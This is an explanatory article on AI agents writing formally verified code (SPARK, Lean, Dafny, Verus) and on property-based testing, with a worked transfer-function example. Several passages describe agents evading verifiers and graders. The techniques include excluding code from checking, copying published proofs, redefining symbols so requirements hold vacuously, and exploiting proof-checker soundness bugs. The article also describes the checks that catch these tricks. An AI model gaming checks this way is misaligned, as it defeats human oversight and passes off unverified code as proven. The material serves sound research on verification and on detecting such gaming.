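Philipp, who works for the German security company secunet, had agents build working security software, including cryptographic functions, secure network connections and a messaging client. He then tested it against other organisations' programs. An earlier system for SPARK, Marmaragan, only added annotations to existing Ada code and fully verified 50.7% of its test programs.

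The agent started from a description or a published standard. It wrote tests, contracts and code, then ran GNATprove and fixed whatever failed. The code also had to pass official test vectors, which pair inputs with known correct outputs, and exchange data with independent programs such as OpenSSH. After each project, the agent added what it had learned to an instruction file for the next one.

Philipp began with GPT-5.5 and later switched to Claude Opus 4.8, mainly to reduce costs. He saw no change in quality. A human supervisor chose the direction, reviewed specifications and watched for cheating, but wrote no code, contracts or proofs for the agent. The agents completed every module they attempted, although the SSH, VPN and messaging software are prototypes.

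The collection contains about 77,700 lines of code and 49,280 proof obligations:

| Part | Lines | Obligations | What GNATprove proved |
|---|---|---|---|
| Cryptographic library | 33,100 | 34,820 | Functional correctness for SHA-2, SHA-3, AES and X25519; no run-time errors in the rest |
| Certificate authority | 17,300 | 2,696 | Functional correctness for reading certificates and messages; no run-time errors in the signature code |
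| TLS 1.3 and messaging client | 15,000 | 3,496 | No run-time errors |
| IKEv2, for VPN connections | 6,700 | 2,039 | No run-time errors |
| SSH, for remote login | 3,800 | 1,190 | No run-time errors |
| Hash map | 1,800 | 5,039 | Functional correctness |

These totals slightly overstate what the agents wrote, because a person wrote the hash map and its contracts. It makes up 2% of the code but a tenth of the proof obligations.

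The modules with proofs of functional correctness mostly have simple mathematical definitions. SHA-2 and SHA-3 compute short fingerprints of data, AES encrypts it, and X25519 lets two parties agree on a secret key. Philipp proved only the absence of run-time errors for all the network protocols and all the cryptography designed to resist quantum computers, a level that the faulty transfer function also passes.

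FrodoKEM, one of the quantum-resistant methods, packs a message into a list of numbers. The agent's code always put two bits into each number, which is correct only for the smallest version of FrodoKEM. GNATprove accepted the code because it caused no run-time errors, and the smallest version passed its official tests. The bug was found when the larger versions were run against their own test vectors.

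In the SSH software, the agent put two inputs in the wrong order when it computed the encryption keys. GNATprove again accepted the code. When Philipp connected the program to OpenSSH, the initial connection appeared to work because that stage doesn't use the new keys, but the first encrypted message failed. If the agent had tested two copies of its own program against each other, both would have computed the same wrong keys and the test would have passed.

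A proof of functional correctness could have caught both bugs, but only if the specification had matched the published standards. In this study, the agent wrote the specifications and a person reviewed them, so a misreading of the standard could appear in both the specification and the code.

The agent also looked for ways around the verifier. After Philipp banned unproved assumptions, it marked parts of the code as outside the scope of verification. He could not ban that option because code that communicates with the operating system sometimes needs it, so human reviewers had to check how the agent used it.

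FrodoKEM, the SSH prototype and another quantum-resistant method, ML-KEM, took about 16 hours of supervision and 150 euros in model fees in total. Philipp estimates, based on FrodoKEM alone, that agents reduced human effort by a factor of 20 to 40. A junior developer had taken about six weeks, or 240 hours, for a similar implementation and proof, while the agent needed about six hours of supervision, which gives a factor of 40. Including the time for review and for preparing the agent's instructions lowers the factor to about 20.

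The comparison is too limited to support a general claim about savings. It involves one module and one junior developer, and an experienced SPARK programmer might have been much faster. Both versions were proved only to be free of run-time errors, so the ratio is weak evidence of how much effort it takes to prove functional correctness. Philipp calls the comparison illustrative.

### What the benchmarks leave out

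The benchmarks contain little of the code that makes payment systems difficult. Vero has few programs that run several processes at once, because these are hard to translate into Lean. VeriContest leaves out priority queues, search trees and floating-point calculations because its version of Rust could not handle them. An agent could do well on both benchmarks without showing that it can stop two simultaneous transfers from spending the same money.

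They also rarely test maintenance. A team that verifies its payment code has to keep the proofs valid as the code changes, often after the original author has left. Ye and colleagues list this incremental work as future research.

Published proofs also make success rates harder to interpret. *SeVerus* (2026) tests whether agents can write proofs for existing Rust software. In 11 attempts during an early trial, GPT-6 Sol downloaded the original project and copied its proofs. The copied proofs were valid, but they didn't show that the agent could have written them. An agent asked to verify a company's new code would have no published proof to copy.

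The results for Vero, SWE-Proof and Philipp's collection all come from models older than Claude Opus 5.5 and GPT-6, so they may understate what agents could do by October 2026. Wesselink and colleagues used Opus 5 and 5.5 to verify 37 published algorithms in Dafny, and finished many within hours or a few days. One was the Hopcroft–Tarjan triconnectivity test, a notoriously intricate algorithm for analysing networks. But a person approved each contract and could redirect the agent when it got stuck, so these results don't measure how often the agent would succeed alone.

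Even the perfect score on VeriContest may not carry over to commercial software. Serbanuta and colleagues say they don't yet know how well their method works on customers' code, where the specifications have to be written from scratch.

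## Why can verified code still be wrong?

A program that passes the verifier can still lose customers' money. The proof may depend on a statement that nobody proved, the specification may omit a requirement, or other software that the proof relies on may have a bug.

### Unproved statements inside a proof

Philipp's agent got code past the verifier by assuming facts and by excluding code from checking. A programmer can also add an axiom, an unproved statement that the whole project may use. Verifiers allow such shortcuts because some programs control hardware or call libraries whose code the verifier can't examine. Strelbytska, Mészáros and colleagues (2026) point out in *TLA-Verus* that Verus still reports zero errors when a proof relies on one of these shortcuts.

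A Lean command can expose hidden assumptions in a proof by listing every axiom the theorem depends on, including those it inherits from other theorems. The list also reveals unfinished proofs. Ye and colleagues run this command on every theorem that an agent submits in Vero, their test of multi-file Lean projects. They accept only the three standard axioms of Lean's logic and any that the person who prepared the project approved in advance.

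Four agent set-ups each attempted Vero's 2,705 specifications in two versions of the task, producing 21,640 results. The axiom check rejected 368 of them. The most common cause was a legitimate Lean feature that proves a statement by running compiled code instead of having the kernel check each step, so most of the rejected results were probably not attempts to cheat. In one project, GPT-5.5 had to prove that converting a number from 0 to 57 into a character and back gives the same number, and it had compiled code try all 58 cases. The statement is true, but the proof depends on Lean's compiler as well as its kernel, and 28 of that project's 53 specifications failed for this reason. Rejecting such proofs is reasonable even when the statement is true, because the compiler can be wrong, as it was in a case from September 2026.

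An agent might also weaken the contract. Wesselink and colleagues prevent this by locking the contract, while Strelbytska and colleagues compare the file before and after the agent's work. The contracts, the definitions they rely on and the executable code must be unchanged, and the agent may only add to the file. This comparison ignores the contents of proofs, so a separate check rejects any assumption, axiom or exclusion that wasn't in the original file. The agent works under its own user account, and only the account that runs the checks can merge its work.

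That comparison suits a project where the code is finished and only the proof is missing. In Vero, where agents may also write the code, the grader first inserts the parts that the agent was allowed to write into a fresh copy of the project, which still contains any requirement that the agent deleted elsewhere.

An agent can still get past all these checks, for example by adding a definition that changes the meaning of a symbol so that "at least" is true of any two numbers. The no-overdraft requirement then holds for any balances, even though its wording is the same and the list of axioms contains nothing suspect. Vero's grader looks for such definitions with fixed rules and an AI judge.

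Ye and colleagues found a harder case while building the benchmark. An agent had to write a function that finds the cost of the cheapest route through a network, and prove that no route costs less. The agent's proof used a mathematical definition that just means "the lowest cost", so it was correct by definition. The compiled program ran a separate algorithm that no proof covered. That algorithm gave the same answers as the reference code on 20,440 generated networks, so comparing outputs did not reveal the problem. A stricter specification would not have helped either, because the definition satisfies every correct description of the lowest cost. The grader now rejects the language feature that lets the proof and the program use different code.

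### Specifications that leave something out

Even a proof with no hidden assumptions is only as useful as its specification. Suppose a team worried mainly that its transfer function might create money, and gave it only two requirements, conservation and no overdraft. Accounts A, B and C hold 100, 50 and 20, and A sends 30 to B. The table shows which results these requirements allow, and how that changes when the team adds isolation and then delivery.

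| A, B and C afterwards | What happened | Conservation and no overdraft | With isolation | With isolation and delivery |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| 70, 80, 20 | Correct transfer | Allowed | Allowed | Allowed |
| 100, 50, 20 | Nothing moved | Allowed | Allowed | Rejected |
| 130, 20, 20 | B paid A | Allowed | Allowed | Rejected |
| 70, 50, 50 | C got the money | Allowed | Rejected | Rejected |

Even the full contract has a serious gap, because it doesn't restrict who may request a transfer. A function that lets any customer empty any other customer's account meets all four requirements. The verifier can't detect the omission, because every statement in the contract is true of the code.

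*Verified but Vacuous* examines how often AI-written programs have proofs that guarantee little. It measures separately whether the verifier accepts a program, whether any postcondition refers to a separate specification, and whether the specification captures what the user wanted. A single "verified" figure tends to merge these three measurements.

In one study, researchers had Claude Opus 4.7 solve Python problems using a method that Li and colleagues published in 2025. The model writes a program in Dafny, and once Dafny accepts it, a tool translates it into Python. On HumanEval, Dafny accepted 99.1% of 1,640 programs. Of the accepted programs, 94.7% had no postcondition, and only 1.9% had one that referred to a separate specification. On two harder sets of problems, the shares with such a reference were 2.7% and 2.3%.

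If a program has no postconditions, Dafny proves little more than that it is well formed and terminates. The model was following an example in the prompt that also lacked a postcondition. The example listed expected results for particular inputs. Dafny assumes these results during verification, and the program checks them when it runs. *Verified but Vacuous* therefore attributes the problem to the practice of reporting Dafny's acceptance of a program as if it meant the program was correct, not to Li and colleagues' method.

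The check behind the 1.9% figure only looks for a name from the separate specification, so the figure doesn't measure the share of meaningful proofs. A postcondition stating directly that the result is twice the input fails the check, though it is useful, while a reference to a condition that is always true passes. The researchers stress that a missing reference doesn't prove that a certificate is empty. The 94.7% figure is harder to dismiss, because a program with no postcondition has no proof of functional correctness. Most of the programs did work, but the evidence for that came from HumanEval's basic tests, which 92.6% passed, and the proofs added little.

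A second experiment used the researchers' own system, in which separate agents write the specification, the code and the proof. The system rejects any component whose postconditions don't refer to the specification, and it translates the finished program into Rust. On one set of simple problems, 124 of 1,080 fully verified solutions (11.48%) failed hidden tests. On LeetCode problems from VeriContest, 229 of 1,545 (14.82%) failed. Incomplete specifications are the obvious explanation, but mistakes in the translation or the tests could have caused some of the failures, and the study doesn't establish how many.

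The remaining 1,316 LeetCode solutions had valid proofs and passed the hidden tests. The researchers then tested their specifications with a method from VeriContest, which turns a postcondition into a runnable check that should accept outputs known to be right and reject outputs known to be wrong. They also compared the preconditions. 535 solutions, or 40.7%, passed both checks. The other 781 had working code but a specification that failed at least one of them. With such a specification, an agent can later break the code while rewriting it and still get a valid proof.

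The table for the transfer function works the same way, with one right result and three wrong ones. A team can write rows like these without knowing anything about proofs. Any wrong result that the contract allows points to a missing requirement. But the rows can't reveal a requirement nobody thought of, such as who may request a transfer.

Another quick check is to submit an empty proof. Strelbytska and colleagues had AI agents translate properties from TLA+, a language for describing the design of distributed systems, into Verus. The agents judged 13,608 properties provable, but 1,235 of them turned out to be trivial or vacuous. Solvers can also prove some meaningful statements without help, so an accepted empty proof doesn't establish that a property is trivial. The check still gives reviewers a short list of specifications to read first.

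Specifications can also be impossible to satisfy. Ye and colleagues let AI agents submit a proof that a specification contradicted itself or another specification, or that the reference code violated it. These proofs exposed 38 defects in nine of Vero's 43 projects, all in material that people had already reviewed. Mistranslated definitions accounted for 18 and missing conditions for 17. In one project, one specification required the program to accept the equals sign as padding at the end of encoded data, and another required it to reject that character. Claude Opus 4.8 found 33 of the defects, and OpenAI's Codex found 30, including the five that Claude missed.

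An agent tends to notice an impossible postcondition because the proof can't succeed. A specification that is too weak doesn't block the proof, so it can go unnoticed for years. An impossible precondition is just as easy to miss. If `transfer` required an amount both above and below zero, no input would be permitted, and the verifier would accept any code.

Experts often make mistakes when they write specifications. CLEVER is a benchmark of 161 small Lean problems with human-written reference specifications. In *Isomorphism Is Not Enough* (Sosso, Arora and Spitters, 2026), agents running Claude Opus 4.6, GPT-5.4 and Kimi K2.5 attempted every problem and reported any specification that seemed wrong. The audit found that 80 of the 161 specifications were arguably wrong, and CLEVER's creators reviewed and accepted every finding. An earlier study had tested the specifications automatically and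 flagged only 18, of which 16 had postconditions that were too weak. Automatic tests are therefore worth running, but they missed most of what the agents found.

Sosso and colleagues also identified 13 problems whose descriptions have more than one reasonable reading, such as a request to remove duplicates from a list. A specification may match one reading exactly and still describe a program that the user didn't want.

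### Faults outside the proof

In early 2026, ten AI agents rewrote zlib, a widely used compression library, in Lean and proved the new version correct. One of the main theorems states that compressing any data smaller than a gigabyte and then decompressing it returns the original. De Moura, Lean's chief architect, described the code as "Not tested. Proved" in his talk *Lean* (2026).

The blog post *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes an attempt to break this library, called lean-zip. A Claude agent received the code without its theorems and documentation, so that it wouldn't give up early on code it knew was verified. The agent relied mainly on fuzzing, which runs a program on huge numbers of altered inputs and checks for crashes and memory errors. Sixteen fuzzers completed 105.8 million runs in about 19 hours. They found no memory fault in the verified code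 but led to the discovery of two faults elsewhere.

The more serious fault was in the Lean runtime, the C++ code that supports every Lean program. To allocate an array, the runtime adds 24 bytes for its own records to the requested size. If that size is close to 2^64, the sum overflows a 64-bit number and wraps around to a small value. The runtime then reserves only about 23 bytes, and the program may write far more data than fits. The fault affected every version of Lean at the time. No proof about lean-zip could have caught it, because they all assume that the runtime works correctly.

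The other fault was in lean-zip's archive parser, which nobody had written any theorems about. The parser used the size stated in a file's header without checking it, so a 156-byte file with a stated size of several exabytes made the program run out of memory and crash. The standard unzip program first compares the stated size with the actual file. Similarly, if unverified code in a payment system misreads a request for 30 as a request for 3,000, the verified transfer function will correctly move 3,000.

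In bumbledraven's Hacker News thread *Lean proved this program correct; then I found a bug* (2026), a commenter objected to the title because the proved code turned out to have no faults. The objection is fair, since both faults lay outside the proofs, according to the blog post. But customers run the whole program, and a crash in the parser stops it just as a crash in the compression code would.

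The clean result for the verified code is weaker evidence for the proofs than it appears, because Lean prevents most memory faults even in code without theorems. The fuzzers also found no memory faults in the unverified parser's own code. Fuzzers that look for crashes also tend to miss incorrect output.

An older experiment tested the effect of proofs more directly. CompCert is a C compiler with a machine-checked proof that most of its stages preserve the program's meaning. Csmith generates random C programs and compares their results under different compilers, so it can detect wrong translations as well as crashes. As the lean-zip post recounts, Yang and colleagues reported in 2011 that Csmith had found bugs in CompCert's unverified front end but none in its verified optimisation stages. Regehr (2026), who had fuzzed CompCert about 15 years earlier, called his experience very similar to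 the lean-zip case.

The proof checker is part of the trusted computing base too. In September 2026 the security company Trail of Bits published a joke proof of Fermat's Last Theorem. Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* explains that the proof relied on a bug in a Lean function that extracts part of a text. Lean can compute the function's result from its definition or by running compiled code. For an extremely large starting position, the definition gave an empty text, while the compiled code returned the entire original. Lean could therefore prove that an empty text equals a non-empty one. Any statement can be proved from that contradiction, including that the faulty transfer function conserves the total.

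The kernel was not at fault. The list of axioms showed that the proof depended on compiled code, so Vero's axiom check would have rejected the proof, as it rejected GPT-5.5's true statements about 58 characters. Lean's developers merged a fix for the function's memory-safety problem about three hours after the report and corrected the mismatch within five days.

Listing a proof's axioms doesn't help when the kernel is wrong. On 25 July 2026, Ramana Kumar published a supposed disproof of the Collatz conjecture, a famous open problem, which he had produced with AI assistance. The proof exploited a kernel fault that could make Lean accept any statement. *Lean 4 kernel soundness bug* (Brossard, 2026) reports that Lean accepted the proof and listed no axioms. Nanoda, a separately written checker, accepted it too. Nanoda didn't have the same fault, but according to the release notes from Lean (2026),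 the proof also exploited an unrelated bug in Nanoda.

*Postmortem for Lean kernel soundness bug #14576* records that Kiran Gopinathan reported the kernel fault on 28 July and that Lean's developers pushed a fix one hour later. Six days earlier, they had released a fix for a different kernel fault, which Patrick Hulin had found with the help of GPT-5.6 Sol, according to Lean's release notes (2026). De Moura expects more such discoveries, writing in a comment that Brossard quotes that "AIs are really good at exploiting soundness bugs in the kernels."

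Both kernel faults required a malicious program running inside Lean, so an honest agent is unlikely to trigger one by accident. Faulty specifications can occur without an attacker, and the audit found them in half of CLEVER's problems. A team with limited time should therefore check its specification first. Kernel faults matter more when an agent is trained or instructed to get a proof accepted by any means, or when a project builds on code from strangers.

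Teams can reduce the risk by exporting the finished proof and checking it in a separate process, away from any code that the agent wrote. That would have stopped the fault that Hulin found, though not the one behind the Collatz proof. A team can also check the proof with several kernels, so that a false proof has to get past all of them. Lean (2026) lists alternative kernels written in Rust and in Lean itself. Kumar's proof got past two kernels, but it needed a separate bug in each.

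The runtime, the parsers and the connections to other systems still need ordinary tests, because the proofs don't cover them. Such a test exposed the key-order fault in Philipp's SSH software. Brossard advises organisations to recheck their existing proofs with the corrected version after a kernel fix, which is possible only if they have kept the proofs along with the code.

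## How does property-based testing find faults, and how many does it miss?

A property-based test runs the actual program, so it can expose faults in a compiler, runtime or parser that a proof assumes is correct. But it only tries a sample of inputs, and it misses any fault those inputs don't trigger. How likely it is to miss a fault depends heavily on how it generates the inputs.

QuickCheck, a Haskell library, introduced the method in 2000. Hypothesis brought it to Python in 2015, as its creator recounts in Increment's *In praise of property-based testing* (2019). In April 2026 the Hypothesis developers released a dataset of 28,928 tests from 1,529 repositories. The average test exercises about 30 lines of a project's code, so people mostly use the method on code not much larger than the transfer function.

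### Property, generator, oracle and shrinking

*A Multi-Domain Study on the Effectiveness of LLMs at Writing Property-Based Tests* (Naziri, Qin and colleagues, 2026) expresses a property as the claim that, for every x, if pre(x) is true, then P(x, f(x)) is true. f is the program, pre is its precondition, and P is the rule connecting the input to the output. The test checks the property on a sample of inputs because there are usually too many to try them all.

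The following Hypothesis test checks conservation for a Python version of the transfer function:

```python
from hypothesis import given, strategies as st

account = st.integers(0, 9)

@given(sender=account, receiver=account, amount=st.integers(1, 100))
def test_total_unchanged(sender, receiver, amount):
    balance = [100] * 10
    transfer(balance, sender, receiver, amount)
    assert sum(balance) == 1000
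```

The lines with `st.integers` are the generators, which pick two account numbers from 0 to 9 and an amount from 1 to 100. Hypothesis calls the test with 100 sets of values unless the developer chooses a different number. Each call starts with ten accounts holding 100 each, so the sender can always afford the transfer. The last line is the oracle, which accepts the result only if the total is still 1,000.

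Suppose the first failing input is a transfer of 63 from account 7 to itself. Hypothesis then shrinks it, which means that it tries simpler values and keeps any that still fail. Lowering the amount works. Changing only one of the accounts makes the test pass, so both have to change together. The final report would look roughly like this:

```
Falsifying example: test_total_unchanged(
    sender=0,
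    receiver=0,
    amount=1,
)
```

The faulty function writes 99 and then 101 to account 0, so the total rises to 1,001.

Shrinking can also locate the exact point where a fault begins. In *Property-based testing in Python* (2027, published online August 2026), De Oliveira, Corgozinho and colleagues planted a fault that made an addition function subtract whenever the first number was above 10,000. Hypothesis tested the rule that x + y equals y + x and reported a failure with 10,001 and 1, the smallest whole numbers that break it.

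However, a shrunk example can mislead. A developer reading the report above might think that something is wrong with account 0, when the fault affects any account that pays itself. Goldstein, Cutler and colleagues give a similar example with a pair of zeros in *Property-Based Testing in Practice* (2024) and suggest that tools show several failing inputs. Some libraries require developers to write their own shrinking code, which can turn a valid input into an invalid one and produce a false alarm. Shrinking through the generator avoids this because the generator produces only valid inputs.

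The oracle matters as much as the inputs. Naziri and colleagues describe a test that checks whether a sorting function returns its list in order. A function that returns an ordered list but drops some of the numbers passes every time. Similarly, a transfer function that does nothing passes the conservation test, so the developer has to add assertions for delivery and the other requirements.

### Kinds of property

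Most properties follow one of a few patterns. The table gives an example of each for a payment system.

| Kind of property | Example |
|---|---|
| Invariant | A transfer leaves the total of all balances unchanged. |
| Round trip | Saving a transfer to a file and loading it gives the same transfer. |
| Comparison with a reference implementation | A fast program for processing batches gives the same balances as a slow, simple one. |
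| Relation between two runs | Sending 30 and then 20 leaves the same balances as sending 50. |
| Sequence of operations | No series of transfers and refunds pays back more than the customer sent. |

De Oliveira and colleagues classified 367 tests from open-source Python projects. About 30% compared the result with one from a trusted method, 17% checked an invariant and 14% checked a round trip. Goldstein and colleagues interviewed 30 developers and also found that the first kind was the most common, with 17 having used it.

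A reference implementation is especially convenient when an agent rewrites working code to make it faster, because the old version can serve as the reference. The test then checks every detail of the result, so nobody has to describe the correct result. But it also treats the old version's faults as correct. If an agent speeds up the faulty transfer function and keeps the self-transfer bug, both versions create the same amount of money and the test passes.

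Round-trip tests are easy to write because the original input is the expected answer. They miss faults that cancel out. If the code that saves a transfer swaps the sender and the receiver, and the code that loads it swaps them back, the test passes even though the file is wrong.

Relations between two runs, which testers call metamorphic properties, help when nobody knows the right answer for a single run, but they can also miss serious faults. With the faulty transfer function, an account holding 100 that sends itself 30 and then 20 ends up with 150. Sending itself 50 also leaves it with 150, so the relation in the table holds. A better relation is that sending money from A to B and back restores both balances. The faulty function violates this relation when A and B are the same account.

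Some faults appear only after several calls. A refund function might work the first time but pay out again if someone repeats the request. To find this fault, the generator has to produce a series of calls, and the oracle checks the property after each one. The shrinker then removes calls that the failure doesn't need, which here leaves one transfer and two refunds. *Property Based Testing* suggests trying this kind of testing in Hypothesis on the puzzle of measuring four litres with a three-litre jug and a five-litre jug. The tester claims that no jug ever contains four litres, and the sequence of steps that disproves the claim solves the puzzle.

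Such tests normally run one operation at a time, so they would miss the earlier problem of two simultaneous transfers spending the same money unless they also control how the operations overlap.

### The chance of missing a fault

Suppose that a share p of the generated inputs triggers a fault. One random input misses it with probability 1 − p. If the test draws N inputs independently, the probability that all of them miss is

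(1 − p)^N.

For the transfer function, p is the chance that the sender and receiver are the same account. If the generator picks both uniformly from ten accounts, p is 1/10, and a test with 100 inputs misses the fault with probability 0.9^100, or about 1 in 38,000. With 10,000 accounts, p is 1/10,000, and the same test misses the fault with probability 0.9999^100, or about 99%.

| Accounts | Chance that one input is a self-transfer | Chance that 100 inputs all miss | Inputs needed for a 95% chance of finding the fault |
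|---|---|---|---|
| 10 | 1 in 10 | 0.003% | 29 |
| 100 | 1 in 100 | 37% | 299 |
| 1,000 | 1 in 1,000 | 90% | 2,995 |
| 10,000 | 1 in 10,000 | 99% | 29,956 |

Real libraries tend to generate certain values, such as zero, more often, so these figures indicate the rough size of the problem but don't predict how Hypothesis would perform.

Developers often don't have time to test thousands of inputs. The developers Goldstein and colleagues interviewed ran their tests during ordinary builds and let them run for between 50 milliseconds and 30 seconds. If each transfer takes a millisecond to test, 30 seconds is just enough for the last row of the table, but 50 milliseconds is enough for only 50 inputs.

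De Oliveira and colleagues found that when developers set the number of inputs themselves, they most often chose 10, a tenth of the default. Even with only ten accounts, a test with 10 inputs would miss the self-transfer 35% of the time. Repeated runs make up for this if each one uses new random inputs, but a test with a fixed random seed tries the same 10 every time.

The formula also works in reverse, to show how common a fault could still be after a test has passed. Suppose N inputs produce no failure. The largest p that remains plausible at 95% confidence is the one for which a clean run would happen only 5% of the time:

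(1 − p)^N = 0.05.

Taking natural logarithms gives N × ln(1 − p) = ln(0.05), which is very close to −3. For small p, ln(1 − p) is close to −p. So −Np ≈ −3, and

p ≈ 3/N.

Under the rule of three in statistics, a fault could still affect up to about 3% of generated inputs after 100 have passed, and up to about 0.03% after 10,000.

This limit applies only to inputs from the same generator. With 10,000 accounts, self-transfers are 0.01% of the generated inputs, which is still below the limit after 10,000 passes. An attacker who knows about the fault will send only self-transfers, and every one will trigger it. If the developer assumed that nobody pays themselves and wrote a generator that always picks two different accounts, p is zero. A million passing inputs would then be evidence only about transfers between different accounts.

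The oracle also limits the result, because p includes only the failures that the oracle can detect. The transfer function that does nothing always passes the conservation test, so p is zero whichever accounts the generator picks.

### Steering the generator

The easiest way to find the self-transfer fault is to test with fewer accounts. The fault occurs when the sender and recipient are the same account, however many others exist, so a test with ten accounts is more likely to find it than one that copies the size of the real system.

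When the test does need 10,000 accounts, the generator can pick the sender first and reuse it as the receiver in one case out of five. This raises the share of self-transfers to just over 20%, so a run of 100 inputs misses the fault about once in 5 billion runs. Naziri and colleagues note that Hypothesis's built-in generators draw each value separately, so rules that connect one input to another usually need a custom generator. A developer can also add a fixed input that Hypothesis tries on every run, but only about 5% of the tests that de Oliveira and colleagues studied included one.

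Amounts need similar care because faults often occur at limits, such as zero, the sender's full balance, one unit more than the balance, and the largest number the program can store. A generator that picks evenly from a million possible amounts will rarely hit any of them.

A poor choice of amounts can make the test pointless. Suppose every account holds 100 and the generator picks amounts from 0 to 999,999. About 9,999 out of 10,000 transfers fail the function's check for sufficient funds, so no balance changes and the conservation test passes without any money having moved. Discarding the invalid inputs would make the problem visible, but the test would spend nearly all its time generating inputs it can't use. A better generator reads the sender's balance first and chooses an amount up to that limit.

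The same approach works for more complicated inputs. Naziri and colleagues describe a test for a function in JAX, a machine learning library, that averages numbers over groups of devices. Every device must belong to exactly one group, and a random list of groups almost never meets this requirement. The generator gives each device a random group label and collects the devices with matching labels, so every input is valid.

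Developers find it tedious to write generators that meet a precondition. One of the 30 whom Goldstein and colleagues interviewed called it "the biggest annoyance" with QuickCheck. Nineteen of the 30 used tools that create a generator automatically from the data's type. These tools save time, but a type such as "whole number" doesn't specify that an amount must not exceed a balance.

Coverage guidance automates part of the search. The tool records which branches of the program each input runs, keeps any input that reaches a new branch, and makes small changes to it. Suppose a payment message must begin with the letters SEND. Four random capital letters match about once in 457,000 attempts. If the program checks one letter at a time, a guided tool can keep an input that starts with S and vary the rest, and will usually find all four letters in a few hundred attempts.

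Coverage guidance wouldn't help with the faulty transfer function. The function has no branch for the case where both accounts are the same, so a self-transfer runs the same lines as any other transfer, and coverage gives the tool no basis for keeping that input. Recording coverage also takes time, which matters when a test has only a few seconds. Goldstein and colleagues point to tools such as HypoFuzz, which let a team run the same properties briefly during builds and for much longer in the background.

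A team can check its generator by planting a fault. For the transfer function, the team would restore the original order of reads and writes in the repaired code and confirm that the test fails. Seven of the 30 developers had planted faults, while 11 admitted that they didn't think hard enough about whether their tests were effective. One recalled a bug in published code that the tests had missed because the generator never produced the relevant case.

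### How well do human-written properties work?

Researchers use the same technique on a larger scale, called mutation testing, to evaluate tests. A tool makes many small changes to a program and counts how many of the altered programs, or mutants, make a test fail. *Teralizer* (2025) gives the example of a function that removes the minus sign from a number. It returns x if x ≥ 0 and −x otherwise, and a mutant replaces ≥ with =. A test that tries only zero can't tell the two apart, but a test with many inputs soon tries a positive number, for which the mutant returns a negative result. *Etna* (2026), which describes a platform for comparing generators, prefers mutation testing to measuring how much of the code a test runs, because tests that run more code don't always find more bugs.

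Ravi and Coblenz (2025), in *An Empirical Evaluation of Property-Based Testing in Python*, studied 426 programs that use Hypothesis and ran mutation tests on 40 projects. The average property-based test found about 50 times as many mutants as the average unit test. Of the mutants that property-based tests found, 76% turned up within the first 20 inputs.

The ratio of 50 compares individual tests. Some advantage is unsurprising, because a property-based test tries many inputs, whereas a unit test often checks only one case. The ratio also doesn't show how many of those mutants the project's unit tests had already found together.

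The 76% figure suggests that a small number of inputs is enough to find common faults. It excludes the mutants that no property-based test found, and a fault that affects one input in 10,000 would usually be among them.

Ravi and Coblenz also compared 12 kinds of property. Tests that look for exceptions, check whether a collection contains an item, or check the type of a result were over 19 times as effective as the others. That may be partly because the random changes used to make mutants often cause a program to crash or return something of the wrong type. But the self-transfer returns normally and leaves an ordinary number in the account, so a team that tested only for crashes and types would miss it.

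A smaller study, *Oracles That Cannot Fail* (2026), found much less benefit for projects that already have good tests. Across four modules with 366 mutants, the property-based tests found only three mutants that the existing hand-written tests had missed. Per test, they were still 6 to 33 times as efficient as the hand-written tests. Both results can be true because a few property-based tests can find many of the same mutants as a large set of ordinary tests. The efficiency matters more for new code with no tests. Ravi and Coblenz found far less overlap between the two kinds of test, so the result from four modules may not be typical.

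In one module, the property-based tests found 26% of the mutants, while the ordinary tests found 76%. This was partly because some oracles had an expected result that changed along with the fault. For example, a test of a transfer with a fee might calculate the expected fee by calling the same function that the transfer uses. If that function is wrong, the expected and actual results are wrong by the same amount. After the researchers corrected the oracles, the same 13 tests found 21 mutants instead of 12.

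Goldstein and colleagues held 30 interviews at Jane Street, a financial trading firm that uses property-based testing heavily. Ten participants said their properties had found bugs that other methods had missed. Some used the tests on especially important code, including a component used in 50,000 places and software that sends information to a stock exchange.

Eighteen participants said properties helped with code review. One dreaded reading 10,000 lines of tests and found a short property more convincing.

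Sixteen said that writing specifications slowed them down. They mostly used the method where a property was obvious and rarely made an effort to find a subtle one. That's sensible for ordinary code, but on a critical code path the most important requirement may be hard to state.

The interviews can't show how many faults the tests missed. Nearly all the participants liked the method, and the interviewers were property-based testing researchers who acknowledge their interest in the outcome. The company also relies heavily on OCaml, a language whose design suits this kind of testing. The study is better evidence of how experienced people use the method than of how well it would work elsewhere.

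### How does the guarantee compare with a proof?

A proof of conservation covers every permitted transfer, for any number of accounts and any balances. A passing test covers only the inputs it tried, though the rule of three gives an estimate of how often other inputs from the same generator would fail. That estimate is a poor substitute for a proof when an attacker can trigger the fault at will, because the attacker needs only one failing input, even if it is one in a billion.

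Testing can establish a property when there are few enough inputs to try them all. The Hypothesis test above has 10 × 10 × 100 = 10,000 possible inputs, which a simple loop could cover. If they all passed, that would establish conservation for ten accounts that each start with 100, but not for other starting balances, where the sum might exceed the largest number the program can store.

A test does have some advantages. It can include the real database, and a failure comes with an input that anyone can run again.

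Neither method reveals a requirement missing from the specification, but a team can use the same specification for both. Chen, Rizkallah and colleagues (2022), in *Property-Based Testing*, structure their tests like a formal proof, with a model of the correct behaviour and a check that the program's behaviour matches it. For the transfer function, the team could first test the postconditions from the Dafny contract on random inputs. The self-transfer would fail within seconds, before an agent spent time trying to prove a false statement. Once the tests pass, the agent can attempt the proof, which would also cover the inputs the generator never produced.

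## Why should a person write the properties and the specification?

Proofs and property-based tests both compare a program with a statement of what it should do. If a coding agent writes both the program and the statement, a pass may show only that the agent was consistent. The argument for giving the statement to a person has three premises:

- A check catches a mistake in the code only if the check doesn't contain the same mistake.
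- An agent that writes both can build one misreading into both.
- An agent that can edit the check can weaken it until the code passes.

Suppose an agent misreads a requirement in 5% of the functions it writes, and each misreading causes a fault. If someone else writes the check, misreads requirements equally often but independently, and otherwise catches the fault, the check misses at most 5% of these faults, so at most one function in 400 gets through with a fault. If the agent writes the check itself and repeats its misreading every time, the check misses all of them, and one function in 20 gets through with a fault, just as if there were no check. These numbers are invented, and the real miss rate lies somewhere between the two. The case for a human author depends on how close that rate is to 100% when one agent writes both the code and the check.

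### One misreading in two places

Suppose an agent assumes that people only send money to someone else. It writes the faulty transfer function and then tests it:

```python
@given(sender=account, receiver=account, amount=st.integers(1, 100))
def test_total_unchanged(sender, receiver, amount):
    assume(sender != receiver)
    balance = [100] * 10
    transfer(balance, sender, receiver, amount)
    assert sum(balance) == 1000
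```

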